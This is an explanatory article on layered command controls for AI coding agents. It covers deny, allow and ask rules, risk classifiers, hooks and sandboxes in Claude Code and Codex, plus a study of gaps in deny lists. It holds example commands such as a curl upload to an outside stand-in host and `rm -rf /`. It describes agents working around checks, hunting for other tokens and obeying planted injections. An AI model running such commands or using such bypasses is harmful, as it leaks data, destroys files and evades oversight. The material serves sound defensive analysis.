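# Command Allow Lists, Deny Lists and Risk-Based Approval as Layered Defenses for AI Agents

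## Why an agent's commands pass through several checks

An AI coding agent is a language model with tools that let it read and edit files, search a project, fetch web pages and run shell commands, which are typed instructions that programmers use to operate a computer. Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex are the best-documented examples. Shell access makes these agents useful because a developer can do nearly everything through the shell, but it also makes them dangerous because the same tool that runs a project's tests can wipe a customer database.

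Companies that build agents place several controls between the model and the machine. Rules block or permit commands by pattern. A reviewer, who may be a person or a second model, decides on commands the rules don't settle. A sandbox may sit beneath both, using the operating system to limit the files and network a command can reach.

### From a request to a running command

A language model cannot run anything by itself. It produces text, some of which is a tool call, a structured request that names a tool and supplies its input (for example, the shell tool and the string `pytest`). The program around the model, called the harness, checks the request. If the command passes, the harness starts a shell, and the operating system executes the command with the user account's rights. The harness then adds the output to the text the model works from, and the model produces its next request.

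In *One Goal, Many Commands*, Chen and Lin (2026) find this arrangement of model, harness and tools in Claude Code, Codex and the open-source agent OpenCode. They place the trust boundary at the check because the shell and the programs it calls run whatever they receive without further checks. Without a sandbox, the harness is the last component that can stop a command before it takes effect.

An instruction in a prompt can make a command less likely, but a rule in the harness can block it. Suppose a developer never wants her agent to push code to the main branch. She can say so in the prompt or in CLAUDE.md, a file of standing instructions for Claude Code. This makes a push less likely, but the model may still give the instruction too little weight late in a long session, or follow later text that contradicts it. She can instead write a deny rule, a pattern whose matching commands the harness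 blocks without asking anyone, whatever the model's reason for issuing them. Anthropic explains in its documentation that prompts and CLAUDE.md shape what Claude tries to do, but only the permission settings change what Claude Code allows.

A deny rule matches the text of a command, so it can miss other ways of doing the same thing that a written instruction such as "never push to main" would cover. Anthropic warns that a deny rule covers the form of a command that Claude usually produces and is not a security boundary around the program itself. It therefore makes sense to write both the rule and the instruction.

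### Where dangerous commands come from

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* gives four reasons why an agent might take a dangerous action. The most common theme in the company's examples is overeager action, in which the agent pursues the user's goal in good faith but does more than the user authorized. In one case, adapted from Anthropic's internal incident log, an agent hit an authentication error partway through a task and began searching configuration files for other access tokens, which someone might have issued for different work.

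An agent makes an honest mistake when it misjudges how far an action reaches, for example by deleting a branch it takes to be its own while a colleague is still using it. In a prompt injection, someone plants instructions in content the agent reads in order to redirect it. A project file might contain an instruction to send the project's passwords to a web address "for validation". A misaligned model pursues a goal of its own. In a hypothetical case, it switches off logging so that nobody can see what it does next. When Anthropic introduced the feature, it wrote that it did not then see this kind of misalignment in practice, though it tests every model for it.

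The incident log shows what kinds of things go wrong but not how often, and it comes from the company that sells the product. It is still useful because how strong a check has to be depends partly on where the command comes from. An agent that misjudges a branch will usually issue a deletion command in its ordinary form, which a simple pattern may well catch. With prompt injection, an attacker chooses the command. Chen and Lin assume that this attacker has read the deny rules, which is realistic because many projects keep them in the same repository as the code. A rule that is good enough against mistakes may therefore give very little protection against prompt injection.

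An overeager agent can work around a control even when nobody has attacked it. Anthropic describes an agent whose deployment command failed a preliminary safety check. The agent then retried the command with an option that skips the check.

### The three-way gate and the sandbox beneath it

In the design that Chen and Lin describe, the harness sorts each command into one of three groups before it can run. The harness checks deny rules first and blocks any command that matches one. It runs commands that match an allow rule's pattern without review, and sends everything else to the reviewer. Claude Code also accepts ask rules, which let the owner require approval every time a command matches a given pattern.

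Models have recently begun to replace users as the reviewers of agents' commands. Claude Code used to ask the user to approve most shell commands, but Anthropic found that people who must approve many requests stop reading them closely, a problem known as approval fatigue. *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) announced that new sessions on most of Anthropic's subscription plans switched to a risk classifier in August 2026. This model judges an action's likely effect and whether the user authorized it. In OpenAI's Codex, the user is still the default reviewer, and a separate reviewing agent is an option. OpenAI argues for keeping that agent separate from the one doing the work because training optimizes the working agent to finish tasks, which creates pressure to treat an approval boundary as another obstacle.

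All of this happens before the command starts, and the gate cannot monitor what the command does afterwards. A guide from the University of Vermont distinguishes two paths to a user's files: the built-in file tools, which run inside Claude Code, and the shell with all the programs it launches. A control on one path does not automatically cover the other. For example, according to Anthropic's *Configure permissions*, a deny rule against reading a file applies to the built-in tools and to shell commands that Claude Code recognizes as reading files, but not to a Python script that opens the file directly.

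The sandbox closes this gap because the operating system applies its limits to the command, however it is worded, and to every process the command starts. By default, commands in Codex have no network access and can write only inside the active workspace, which is the current directory plus temporary directories, according to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*. A sandbox can restrict where data goes, but it can't detect whether the user wanted the data to go there. Anthropic adds that sandboxes take a lot of upkeep, since each new capability needs configuring and work that requires the network or the host machine breaks the isolation.

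The two products also combine the gate with the sandbox differently. In its standard setting, Codex runs commands freely inside the sandbox and requests review mainly when a command needs to leave it. In auto mode, Claude Code allows file reads and edits inside the project, but sends the classifier most shell commands that aren't already decided by a rule, whether or not a sandbox is on. Codex therefore depends more on correct sandbox boundaries, while Claude Code depends more on the classifier's accuracy.

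Anthropic recommends using permissions and sandboxing together for "defense-in-depth". NIST, the US standards institute, defines *defense-in-depth* in its glossary as an information security strategy that integrates people, technology and operations to place barriers across multiple layers of an organization. Fraunhofer's *Defence in Depth* collects national definitions, including a plainer one from Oman that describes several layers of security guarding against the failure of a single component.

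### Default-deny and default-allow

Any set of rules leaves some commands unmentioned, and how a system handles those commands matters more than most individual rules. A default-allow system runs them, while a default-deny system blocks them. A deny list on its own is default-allow, so it protects only against what its writers thought to list, as Chen and Lin point out.

The classic argument for default-deny comes from *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975). One of its eight design principles, fail-safe defaults, is to base access decisions on permission rather than exclusion. Designers of large systems will make mistakes, and mistakes in a list of permissions are easier to detect. They tend to block something legitimate, and a user soon complains, whereas a mistake in a list of exclusions tends to let something through, and nobody may notice.

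Massacci objects in *Is ‘deny access’ a valid ‘fail-safe default’ principle* that denying access may not be a sufficient principle for cars and planes. The objection seems weaker for a coding agent. Anthropic reports that when its classifier wrongly blocks something, the agent usually needs only one retry before it finds another route.

A three-way gate asks by default, rather than denying or allowing, so its safety depends on whoever answers. If the reviewer approves nearly everything, the gate behaves like default-allow, and Chen and Lin argue that approval fatigue has caused this wherever users do the reviewing. Claude Code also lets its owner choose default-deny or default-allow. Its `dontAsk` mode denies tools that nobody has approved in advance, while `bypassPermissions` skips the permission prompts (with an exception for deleting the whole disk or home directory). Anthropic advises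 using `bypassPermissions` only in isolated environments.

Complete mediation, another of the 1975 principles, requires a system to check every access to every object. Command rules fall well short of this because they check a line of text once, and that line may start a program that opens a thousand files. A sandbox comes much closer, at least for files and network connections.

### Six commands from one request

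Suppose a developer asks an agent to fix a failing test in a billing application. The agent works on its own branch, in a copy of the code on the developer's laptop, and proposes six commands.

| Command | Effect | What a careful owner would want |
|---|---|---|
| `pytest` | Runs the project's tests | Let it run |
| `python check_totals.py` | Runs a script the agent has just written | Let it run after someone has read the script, or where it can do little harm |
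| `rm -r tmp/test-output` | Deletes a temporary directory | Let it run if this session created the directory; otherwise ask |
| `git push origin fix-totals` | Sends the agent's commits to its working branch on the server | Let it run if the server is the project's own |
| `curl -T test.log paste.example` | Uploads a log to an outside site | Block it, or ask first |
| `python manage.py migrate --database=production` | Changes the structure of the live database | Block it |

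Running the tests is part of the job, although even `pytest` executes code that the agent may have just edited. You can tell almost nothing about the script's effect from the command that starts it, because the effect depends on what is in the file. Whether the deletion is safe depends on what happened earlier, since a directory called `tmp` may hold the only copy of somebody's results. The risk of the push depends on its destination. By default, Anthropic's classifier accepts a push to the session's working branch, and according to Anthropic's configuration guide, it trusts only the working directory and the servers already configured for the repository.

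The upload might help the agent debug, but test logs can contain access tokens or customer records, and nobody can reliably remove them from a public site. Anthropic describes a similar case among its own staff, in which an upload to an internal drive failed and Claude then tried to publish the same report on a public code-sharing site, but the classifier denied it. The migration would change live customer data, which a request to fix a test does not authorize. Anthropic's incident log also includes attempted migrations against a production database.

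### Two ways for a check to be wrong

A check's miss rate, also called its false-negative rate, is the share of dangerous commands that it lets through. Its false-alarm rate, or false-positive rate, is the share of harmless commands that it blocks.

In this example, the upload and the migration count as dangerous, the other four commands count as harmless, and the production database is on another machine. A sandbox without network access stops both dangerous commands, so its miss rate is zero. It also stops the push, which the owner wanted, so its false-alarm rate is one in four. If the sandbox is replaced with a deny rule that blocks only `curl`, there are no false alarms, but the migration goes through, so the miss rate is one in two. Either rate alone would be misleading, since a layer could avoid all misses by blocking everything or all false alarms by blocking nothing.

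In real use, harmless commands vastly outnumber dangerous ones, so even a low false-alarm rate causes many interruptions. Suppose an agent issues 1,000 harmless commands and 10 dangerous ones, and a layer has a false-alarm rate of 5% and a miss rate of 20%. The layer blocks 50 harmless commands and 8 dangerous ones, and lets 2 dangerous ones run. A person who reviews the blocked commands will find that most were harmless, and may conclude that the layer is a nuisance.

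A second layer reduces missed dangerous actions but increases false alarms. If a command must pass two layers that miss 20% and 10% of dangerous actions, and their misses are independent, only 2% get past both. If each layer also blocks 5% of harmless commands, independently of the other, together they block nearly 10%. Independence is a strong assumption, and the three-way gate does not always put a command through both layers. If the developer has an allow rule for everything that begins with `python`, and the harness applies it, the migration runs without reaching the reviewer, so the reviewer's miss rate makes no difference.

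## How a command is matched against rules and given a verdict

An allow rule for everything that begins with `python` lets through a database migration that begins with that word, because the harness only compares text. Before comparing, the harness parses the line to work out its structure and splits it if it holds more than one command. It then matches each command against the rules, combines the results into a verdict for the whole line, and passes anything the rules don't decide to another control. Claude Code and Codex both work in this order, but they differ in how much of a complicated line they take apart and, above all, in what they do with a command that no rule matches.

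### Splitting a line into commands

A harness has to split a command line into separate commands before matching it against rules, because a shell accepts several commands on one line. In `pytest && git push origin fix-totals`, the operator `&&` starts the push only if the tests succeed. With `||` the second command starts only if the first fails, with `;` it starts either way, and `|` feeds the output of one command into the next. If the harness compared the whole example line with a rule that allows everything beginning with `pytest`, the push would run without review.

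Claude Code splits a line at these operators, at two rarer ones (`&` and `|&`) and at line breaks. The line runs without a prompt only if every part matches an allow rule or belongs to a built-in set of read-only commands such as `ls`, `cat` and `grep`. A deny or ask rule applies to the whole line if it matches any part, so a deny rule against `git push` blocks the line above even if the developer has allowed `pytest`. According to Anthropic, deny and ask rules also apply to commands nested inside others, such as those in the body of a loop or in a command substitution, where the shell runs an inner command and inserts its output into the outer one.

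Claude Code also splits compound commands when it saves approvals. If the user approves `git status && npm test` and chooses not to be asked again, it saves a rule only for `npm test`, because `git status` is read-only and doesn't need approval.

Commands that are harmless on their own can be dangerous together, and a harness misses this if it judges each one separately. Claude Code therefore treats a few combinations as special cases. Changing directory is read-only, and so are some forms of `git`, but in Manual mode, where the user is the reviewer, Claude Code prompts the user when the two are combined, because `git` can execute scripts stored in the new directory. It also prompts when a command changes directory and then writes to a file, if it can't determine which directory the file would end up in.

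Codex receives many commands as `bash -lc` followed by a whole script in a single string. According to OpenAI's *Rules*, Codex splits the script only if it is a linear chain of commands made of plain words and joined by `&&`, `||`, `;` or `|`. Codex then parses it with tree-sitter, a widely used parsing library, and applies the rules to each command. In OpenAI's example, `git add . && rm -rf /` becomes two commands, so an allow rule for `git add` can't also approve deleting the whole disk.

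If the script uses redirection, substitution, environment variables, wildcards or control flow such as loops, Codex leaves it whole and matches the rules against a list of three arguments: `bash`, `-lc` and the full script. These features make the script's text an unreliable guide to what will run. A wildcard stands for file names that the shell fills in later, a variable can hold almost anything, and a loop may run one command many times with different arguments. A harness that split such a script and misread one part could approve a command its owner never allowed.

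OpenAI calls this handling conservative, and for allow rules it is. An allow rule for `git add` doesn't match a list that begins with `bash`, so the script gets no special treatment. But a rule that forbids `git push` doesn't match that list either, even when the script contains a push. The sandbox and the approval settings still apply and give useful protection, but they aren't the outright block that the owner wrote. Based on OpenAI's description, an owner could add a rule that asks for approval of everything beginning with `bash -lc`, but this would trigger a prompt for every script with an ordinary redirect. An allow rule on the same prefix would be a serious mistake, because it would exempt every unsplit script from the sandbox.

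### Wrappers and redirections

Some programs exist only to run another program. For example, `timeout 30 pytest` runs the tests and stops them after 30 seconds. Claude Code strips a fixed set of these wrappers before matching, so a rule for `pytest` also covers `timeout 30 pytest`. The set excludes tools that run a command inside a development environment, such as `npx`, `docker exec` and `devbox run`. An allow rule for everything that begins with `devbox run` would therefore approve any command that follows. Anthropic advises writing a separate rule, such as `devbox run npm test`, for each inner command.

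Claude Code does not apply general allow rules to certain wrappers. In Manual mode, it still prompts before running `watch`, which runs a command repeatedly, even if the user has allowed everything that begins with `watch`. The same is true of `find`, a file-search program, when the command includes an option to delete or execute what it finds. To run such a command without a prompt, the user must write a rule containing the exact command. Even that fails if the command contains an asterisk, because Claude Code then reads the rule as a pattern.

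A redirection sends a command's output to a file, as in `pytest > results.txt`. Claude Code checks the target file against the rules for editing files, so an allow rule for `pytest` approves running the tests but not overwriting a file outside the project. Codex, by contrast, doesn't split a script into separate commands if it contains a redirection.

### Two ways to write a pattern

A Codex rule describes the beginning of a command as an ordered list of arguments. The pattern `["git", "push"]` matches any command whose first two arguments are `git` and `push`. One position can hold alternatives, so `["gh", "pr", ["view", "list"]]` covers both viewing and listing pull requests with GitHub's command-line program. The arguments must appear in the listed order with nothing between them. In OpenAI's example, a rule for `gh pr view` does not match a command that has the option `--repo` between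 `pr` and `view`.

Each rule also has a decision of `allow`, `prompt` or `forbidden`, which makes it an allow, ask or deny rule respectively. If the decision is missing, Codex assumes `allow`, so forgetting it produces the most permissive kind of rule. A rule can include a justification, which Codex may show when it blocks the command, and examples, which Codex checks when it loads the file. OpenAI marks the whole feature as experimental.

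In Claude Code's patterns, `*` matches any text, including spaces. A rule without an asterisk matches one exact command. `Bash(git log *)` matches every `git log` command in the shell tool, and `Bash(git *)` matches every `git` command, including pushes. The words before the first asterisk limit a rule the most, and Claude Code warns at startup about an allow rule such as `Bash(git * main)`, where the asterisk replaces the subcommand. That rule accepts any `git` command that ends in the word "main", even if it doesn't involve the main branch. It also accepts any options, including one that makes `git` run a program that the caller names.

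In Claude Code, a single space can change what a rule covers. `Bash(ls *)` matches `ls -la` but not `lsof`, a different program that lists open files, while `Bash(ls*)` matches both. Codex avoids this problem by comparing whole arguments, so `ls` never matches `lsof`, but its prefix rules can't set a condition on the end of a command. Claude Code's patterns are more flexible, which also makes them easier to get wrong. Both notations describe how a command is written, so a rule that matches as designed may still cover more or less than its author intended.

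### When rules disagree

Suppose the developer wants to block every push except one, and writes a deny rule for `git push` and an allow rule for `git push origin fix-totals`. Both rules match the push in the billing example.

Claude Code checks deny rules first, then ask rules, then allow rules, and the first match decides. Codex collects every matching rule and applies the strictest decision. The two methods always give the same verdict because Claude Code checks the strictest rules first, so its first match is also the strictest. In the example, a deny rule and an allow rule both match, so both products block the push.

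Specificity does not affect precedence in either product, so a narrow allow rule cannot override a broad deny or ask rule. The developer has to change the broad rule instead. She could deny only the pushes she considers dangerous, or change the deny rule to an ask rule and approve the occasional acceptable push herself. This is less convenient than writing an exception, but it means that adding allow rules never changes what a deny rule blocks.

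Claude Code's deny lists for files can include exceptions, though an allow rule can't create them. A pattern that begins with an exclamation mark exempts files from the patterns before it in the same deny list. For example, an owner can block every file whose name ends in `.env` and then exempt `sample.env`, which typically holds placeholders instead of real passwords. The exemption works only within one settings file, so a project can't use it to unblock a file that the company has blocked.

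The stricter rule also wins when rules set by different people conflict. In Claude Code, if any settings file denies a command, no other settings file can allow it, whether the deny rule comes from the user, the project or the company's administrators. Codex administrators can likewise impose restrictive rules on everyone. A project's rules need more care because they come with code that a stranger may have written. Claude Code applies a project's deny and ask rules immediately, since they can only restrict, but applies the allow rules only after the user has marked the folder as trusted. Codex loads none of a project's rules until the user trusts the project's configuration.

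### Commands that no rule matches

The two products differ mainly in how they handle commands that match no rule. Under Codex's usual approval policy, `on-request`, an unmatched command runs inside the sandbox and needs approval only to leave it. Codex also has a stricter policy, `untrusted`, under which it asks about every command outside a trusted set, and a `never` policy, under which it doesn't ask at all.

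An allow rule in Codex lets a command run outside the sandbox as well as without a prompt. The rule is therefore useful only for commands that can't finish inside the sandbox. OpenAI explains that the sandbox keeps the `.git` directory read-only even though the rest of the workspace is writable, so `git commit`, which has to write to that directory, must run outside the sandbox. The owner then has to choose between approving each commit and allowing them all with a rule.

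OpenAI's own staff run Codex with the sandbox on. In the configuration shown in *Running Codex safely*, administrators permit only the read-only and workspace-write sandbox modes. Codex can reach expected network destinations there, can't reach unwanted ones, and needs approval for unfamiliar domains.

In Claude Code, an allow rule determines only whether a command needs review, and separate settings control whether the command runs in a sandbox. How Claude Code handles an unmatched command depends on the permission mode, a session-wide setting that the user can change at any time. Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode* describes six modes.

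| Mode | What Claude Code does with an unmatched shell command |
|---|---|
| Manual (`default`) | Asks the user |
| `acceptEdits` | Runs common file commands, such as `mv` and `rm`, inside the working directory; asks about most others |
| `plan` | Sends it to the classifier if auto mode is available; otherwise asks |
| `auto` | Sends it to the classifier |
| `dontAsk` | Blocks it |
| `bypassPermissions` | Runs it, with a few exceptions |

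The built-in read-only commands are a partial exception, since they usually run without a prompt in every mode.

The mode can also change which rules apply. When a session enters auto mode, Claude Code suspends allow rules that would let the agent execute arbitrary code, such as a rule for all shell commands or for every command that begins with `python`, and restores them when the session leaves auto mode. The broad `python` rule therefore approves the production migration in Manual mode, but in auto mode the migration goes to the classifier. A narrow rule like `Bash(npm test)` applies in both modes.

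Claude Code can come close to Codex's arrangement. If the user turns on its sandbox in Manual mode and leaves the default automatic approval on, sandboxed commands generally run without a prompt. This is true even if an ask rule covers the whole shell tool, but an ask rule that names a command, such as `git push`, still triggers a prompt. Much of the difference between the products is therefore in their defaults, which the owner can change.

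### Hooks and the order of checks

Patterns can't express every check an owner might want, so Claude Code also offers hooks, which are programs the owner supplies and Claude Code runs at set points. One type of hook runs before a tool call and receives the full command, so it can apply any logic to it. For example, it can extract a web address from the command and compare it with a list of approved domains. The hook can block the call, force a prompt, or let the call proceed.

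Anthropic gives the full order of evaluation in its guide for developers who build their own agents on Claude Code. Claude Code runs hooks first, then checks deny rules, ask rules, the permission mode and allow rules, in that order. If none of these decides the call, it runs a function that the developer has supplied to answer approval requests. In an ordinary session, it prompts the user instead.

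When a hook blocks a command, the block overrides any allow rule. Claude Code still checks the deny and ask rules when a hook permits a command, so a mistake in the hook can't cancel a prohibition. This makes hooks a practical way to handle exceptions. An owner who wants to allow nearly everything can write one very broad allow rule and use a hook to reject the few commands she worries about, instead of describing all the harmless ones. She then relies on the hook about as much as she would on a deny list.

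Another kind of extension, called a mod, can break the rule that denials always win. A mod returns its verdict after the hooks have run, and it can approve a call that a deny rule or hook has blocked if the machine has no company-managed settings and the session doesn't use a Team or Enterprise login. If the machine has managed settings or the session uses one of those logins, the denial holds by default. Anyone who installs a mod on a personal machine is therefore trusting its author not to override the deny rules.

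The order of evaluation also explains which checks still apply in `bypassPermissions` mode. Deny and ask rules are checked before the permission mode, so deny rules still block and ask rules still prompt. Hooks run even earlier and can also block. Allow rules are checked after the mode has already approved almost everything, so they have no effect. If a developer allows only file reading and then turns on bypass mode, the agent can still run any shell command her deny rules don't mention.

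Some protections don't depend on the owner's rules. Claude Code recognizes attempts to delete the root of the disk, the home directory, the working directory and a few similar targets with `rm` or `rmdir`, and no allow rule or hook can approve them. It asks the user in bypass mode, sends the command to the classifier in auto mode, and blocks it in `dontAsk` mode. Anthropic describes this as a guard against model error and warns that the check can miss some commands.

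In a non-interactive run in bypass mode, Claude Code denies the few calls that would still prompt, because nobody is there to answer. In `dontAsk` mode, it denies every call that matches an ask rule, so an ask rule has the same effect as a deny rule.

### The six commands in both systems

Suppose the developer of the billing application writes three rules: allow `pytest`, ask about `git push`, and deny `curl`. She runs Claude Code in auto mode without a sandbox. She also tries Codex with its default settings, without network access.

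| Command | Matching rule | Claude Code | Codex |
|---|---|---|---|
| `pytest` | Allow | Runs without review | Runs outside the sandbox without review |
| `python check_totals.py` | None | Classifier decides | Runs inside the sandbox without review |
| `rm -r tmp/test-output` | None | Classifier decides | Runs inside the sandbox without review |
| `git push origin fix-totals` | Ask | Asks the developer | Asks the developer; if she agrees, runs outside the sandbox |
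| `curl -T test.log paste.example` | Deny | Blocks it | Blocks it |
| `python manage.py migrate --database=production` | None | Classifier decides; its default rules block production migrations | Starts inside the sandbox and can't reach the database; needs approval to leave |

The allow rule for `pytest` helps her in Claude Code, but in Codex it lets the tests, and any new code they run, execute outside the sandbox. She should delete the rule from Codex unless her tests need the network or files outside the workspace.

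The deletion, by contrast, runs without approval because the directory is inside the workspace, where the Codex sandbox permits writing. It runs even if the directory holds the only copy of somebody's results. To be asked first, the user would need an ask rule for `rm`. Claude Code's classifier can consider the session's history, and by default it blocks the irreversible destruction of files that existed before the session began.

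If she switches Claude Code to Manual mode, it prompts her for each of the three unmatched commands. In bypass mode, all three run, including the migration, but the push still triggers a prompt and the upload stays blocked. Joining commands doesn't help the agent get around the deny rule in either product. Both split `pytest && curl -T test.log paste.example` into two parts and block the whole line because the second part matches the deny rule.

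### What a matching error costs

A rule can fail to match a command that its author meant to cover, and how much this matters depends on the kind of rule. When a deny rule fails to match, the command moves on to the remaining steps, and nobody may notice, as Saltzer and Schroeder warned about lists of exclusions. The command then runs in bypass mode, while in auto mode a classifier has to catch it.

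When a narrow allow rule fails to match, Claude Code asks the user in Manual mode and consults the classifier in auto mode. In Codex, the command runs inside the sandbox even though the user expected it to run outside. These mismatches are inconvenient, and the extra prompts add to approval fatigue, but each error is visible and does little harm.

A deny rule that matches too many commands blocks harmless work, which the owner soon notices, while an allow rule that matches too many lets dangerous commands skip review. A harness should therefore match deny rules broadly and allow rules narrowly, even if the same pattern then means slightly different things in the two lists.

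Claude Code matches deny rules more broadly than allow rules in several cases. A programmer can set a variable for a single command by writing it in front, as in `NODE_ENV=test npm test`. An allow rule for `npm test` matches this command only if the variable is on a short list of safe ones, because some variables change how a program behaves. A deny rule matches regardless of the variable. For symbolic links, which are file names that point to another file, an allow rule applies only if both the link and the file behind it match, while a deny rule applies if either does. The file pattern `src/**` covers only the `src` folder at the top of the current directory in an allow rule, but covers folders of that name at any depth in a deny rule.

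When Codex does not split a complicated script, both allow rules and deny rules stop matching the commands inside it. The sandbox then blocks a forbidden action only if that action needs something the sandbox withholds. It would stop a forbidden upload, which needs the network, but not a forbidden deletion inside the workspace.

### When the harness and the shell read a command differently

Rule matching assumes that the harness and the shell interpret a command the same way. Security advisories and a survey from 2026 report command filters that interpreted a command differently from the shell that then ran it. In such cases even a correct rule doesn't help, because the harness isn't applying it to the command that the shell executes.

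A semicolon normally ends a shell command, but inside quotation marks it's an ordinary character. Quoted text can also contain a substitution, which holds another command that may have its own quotation marks. A filter that searches for semicolons with a simple text pattern will therefore split some lines in the wrong place and fail to split others that it should. Shells also differ. Windows PowerShell has a different grammar from Bash and gives many of its commands several names.

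The harness should parse the line with a real parser for the shell being used, so that it finds the same commands the shell will find. Codex uses tree-sitter for this, and Claude Code parses PowerShell into a syntax tree and expands common aliases into full command names before matching rules. If the parser fails, the harness should treat the command as unsettled. In Manual mode, Claude Code asks for approval when it can't fully parse a command, and always asks when a command is longer than 10,000 characters, the limit of its analysis. Allow rules also don't apply to an unfinished line that ends in `&&`.

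A correct parser still can't determine what a line will contain after the shell fills in its variables and wildcards. A wildcard might expand to a filename that looks like an option, and some programs have options that delete files. Claude Code therefore prompts in Manual mode when an unquoted wildcard appears with such a program, even though the program normally counts as read-only. It also prompts when a command changes `PATH`, the list of directories where the shell looks for programs, because a familiar name such as `ls` could then start a different program.

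The protection these prompts provide depends on how they are answered. In `dontAsk` mode, Claude Code denies any command that would otherwise trigger a prompt, including one it can't read. Under Codex's `never` policy, Codex doesn't prompt anyone, so the sandbox is the only remaining protection against a script it can't split.

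## What deny lists miss and what allow lists let through

A deny rule can fail even when the harness parses every line and applies every rule correctly, because the rule describes how a command is written, while its author cares about what the command does. The developer of the billing application denies `curl` because she doesn't want project data to leave her laptop, but many other programs on the laptop can also send data. Chen and Lin leave matching errors out of their study because they want to show that deny lists fail even when the matching is flawless.

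*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) points out that the mismatch between commands and effects runs in both directions. One command can also have many different effects, so an allow rule can approve far more than its author intended.

*AI Coding Agents in Social Science* (2026) includes a guide to configuring Claude Code, with a settings file described as blocking all web access. The file denies the two built-in web tools and three shell commands (`curl`, `wget` and `fetch`) but allows every other shell command, so its rules let through any other program that can open a network connection. The file also turns on the sandbox, so whether the agent can reach the web depends on the sandbox's network settings.

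### What makes a deny list incomplete

To measure this problem, Chen and Lin needed to work out what each deny list was meant to block without asking its author. They start by defining an operation as a change to some part of the machine's state, such as its files. Formally, an operation is a function *o* from states to states, and a command performs *o* if running it takes the machine from state *s* to state *o(s)*. Two commands that work in different ways perform the same operation if they leave the machine in the same state.

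A deny list blocks an operation if it stops at least one command that performs the operation. It fully blocks the operation if it stops every such command on the machine, with any arguments, and incompletely blocks it if at least one gets through. Chen and Lin call a command that gets through a bypass. A bypass can be an ordinary program doing what its manual describes, with no bug or exploit involved.

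One of Chen and Lin's examples is a list of six deny rules from an open-source project. Each rule names a familiar program that prints text, such as `cat` or `head`, and applies when the command mentions a file with `.env` in its name. Developers often keep passwords in such files. The list only partly blocks printing these files, because other standard programs can print them too. Chen and Lin don't count printing the project's README file as a gap, because the list has no rule against it.

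This definition relies on inferring a list author's intent from a single blocked command. Chen and Lin defend it by arguing that anyone who wants to prevent an operation will think of at least one command that performs it, and that list authors keep their lists short because broad ones get in the way of work. Both points are plausible, but the inference can be wrong. An owner may deny a download program to prevent network traffic, but because the program can also save a file, her list would count as an incomplete attempt to block file creation. Chen and Lin acknowledge that they count a list aimed at code execution as one aimed at several file operations. Their results may therefore overstate how often list authors fall short of their own goals, and only interviews with those authors could show by how much.

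### How Chen and Lin searched for gaps

The search program ShellSieve uses a language model, Claude Sonnet 4.6, to propose ways around a list, then runs each proposal to see if it works. The model receives a command's help text and manual, along with any entry for that command in a public catalogue of ways to misuse standard programs. It then proposes arguments that might make the command perform one of seven file operations without being joined to another command.

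ShellSieve then creates fresh files in a sandbox and runs the proposal. To test whether a command can read a file, it places a unique marker in the file and checks whether the marker appears in the output. To test deletion, it checks whether the file is gone. If the test fails, the model receives the error message and can revise its proposal up to five times.

ShellSieve applies the same procedure to the commands a list blocks and to the other programs on a standard Debian Linux installation. An unblocked program that can perform a blocked operation is a bypass. The whole evaluation took three hours and cost $25 in model use. An attacker who had read a project's deny list could presumably search it for gaps even more cheaply.

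A language model can easily invent an option that doesn't exist, but the individual findings are trustworthy because every bypass that ShellSieve reported had worked when executed on the test machine. The model can't generate every possible bypass, so Chen and Lin describe their counts as a lower bound.

They collected 1,709 lists with 13,332 rules, about eight per list, from public projects on GitHub (their introduction gives 1,731 lists in one place). A thousand of the lists are for Claude Code, sampled at random from more than 24,000 projects, and the rest are for OpenCode (573) and Codex (136). Nearly all come from projects with fewer than 100 stars, GitHub's measure of popularity. The sample is therefore good evidence about individual developers and small projects, but weak evidence about the rules that companies impose on their staff, which don't normally appear in public projects.

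### How incomplete the lists are

Chen and Lin found that 69.0% to 98.6% of the lists that block an operation at all block it incompletely, depending on which of the seven operations it is. The share stays above 44.4% at every level of project popularity and above 46.2% for each of the three agents. Projects with at least 1,000 stars have the lowest share for four of the operations, but this may be chance because only 11 lists come from such projects.

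Chen and Lin also counted how many commands an owner would have to add to a list to block each operation fully.

| Operation | Fewest missing commands | Average | Most |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read a file | 200 | 217 | 222 |
| Write to a file | 5 | 97 | 106 |
| Create a file | 63 | 98 | 180 |
| Delete a file | 38 | 54 | 58 |
| Copy a file | 27 | 39 | 40 |
| Change a file's permissions | 1 | 3 | 13 |
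| Change a file's owner or group | 7 | 11 | 12 |

The average of 217 applies only to reading files. A list needs 180 more commands on average, and 603 in the worst case, to close every gap in everything it is meant to block. The narrow range for reading, 200 to 222, suggests that careful authors get hardly any closer to a complete list than careless ones, because too many programs can print a file. A list against changing file permissions usually lacks only a few commands, so an owner could realistically complete it.

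These counts assume that the owner adds programs one at a time, but a single rule can sometimes cover many programs. A pattern in Claude Code can begin with an asterisk, so one deny rule could match every command whose text contains `.env`. This would close many of the gaps in the six-rule list, but it would also block a harmless commit whose message mentions the file, and it would still miss a command that reaches the file without naming it. Deletion has no obvious equivalent, because the dangerous part is usually the action and not a particular file name.

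Anthropic warns that rules that try to restrict a command's arguments are fragile. Its example is a pattern meant to limit `curl` to a single website, which fails to match if an option comes before the address or if the address is in a variable. A deny rule written this way would miss some of the commands it was meant to block.

### Why authors leave commands out

Chen and Lin tested three possible causes and consider two of them confirmed. One is that people who write the lists leave out commands they haven't heard of. To test this, they ranked commands by how widely Debian users have them installed, and found that less popular commands are more likely to be bypasses. The pattern is strong for reading, writing and creating files, but popularity makes almost no difference for deletion.

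The other is versatility. An author may know that a command can do harm but leave it off the list because it has many legitimate uses. Commands that can perform several of the seven operations bypass a median of 664 lists, compared with 281 for commands that can perform only one. The difference is statistically significant, though small by the usual convention. It is also weak evidence of why authors omit commands. A command that can both read and delete files can get past lists aimed at either operation, so it would bypass more lists even if authors chose their entries at random.

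Chen and Lin reject a third explanation, that list authors miss commands because the dangerous ability is hidden. Of the commands whose short reference page mentions an operation, 40.1% are bypasses for it, compared with 5.7% of commands whose page doesn't. This comparison is flawed too, because many commands in the second group can't perform the operation. It still shows that list authors often miss abilities described in the most basic documentation.

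Gaps in deny lists have different causes, which need different fixes. If the people writing the lists simply didn't know which commands were dangerous, someone could publish a long standard list for everyone to copy. But that list wouldn't help with a versatile program that developers use every day, because blocking it would interrupt too much ordinary work.

### How much an incomplete list still protects

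The study covers only seven file operations. Chen and Lin left out network activity because testing it would require simulated servers, so their percentages don't apply to the upload in the billing example. They also left out code execution as a separate operation because it leaves no single trace in the file system.

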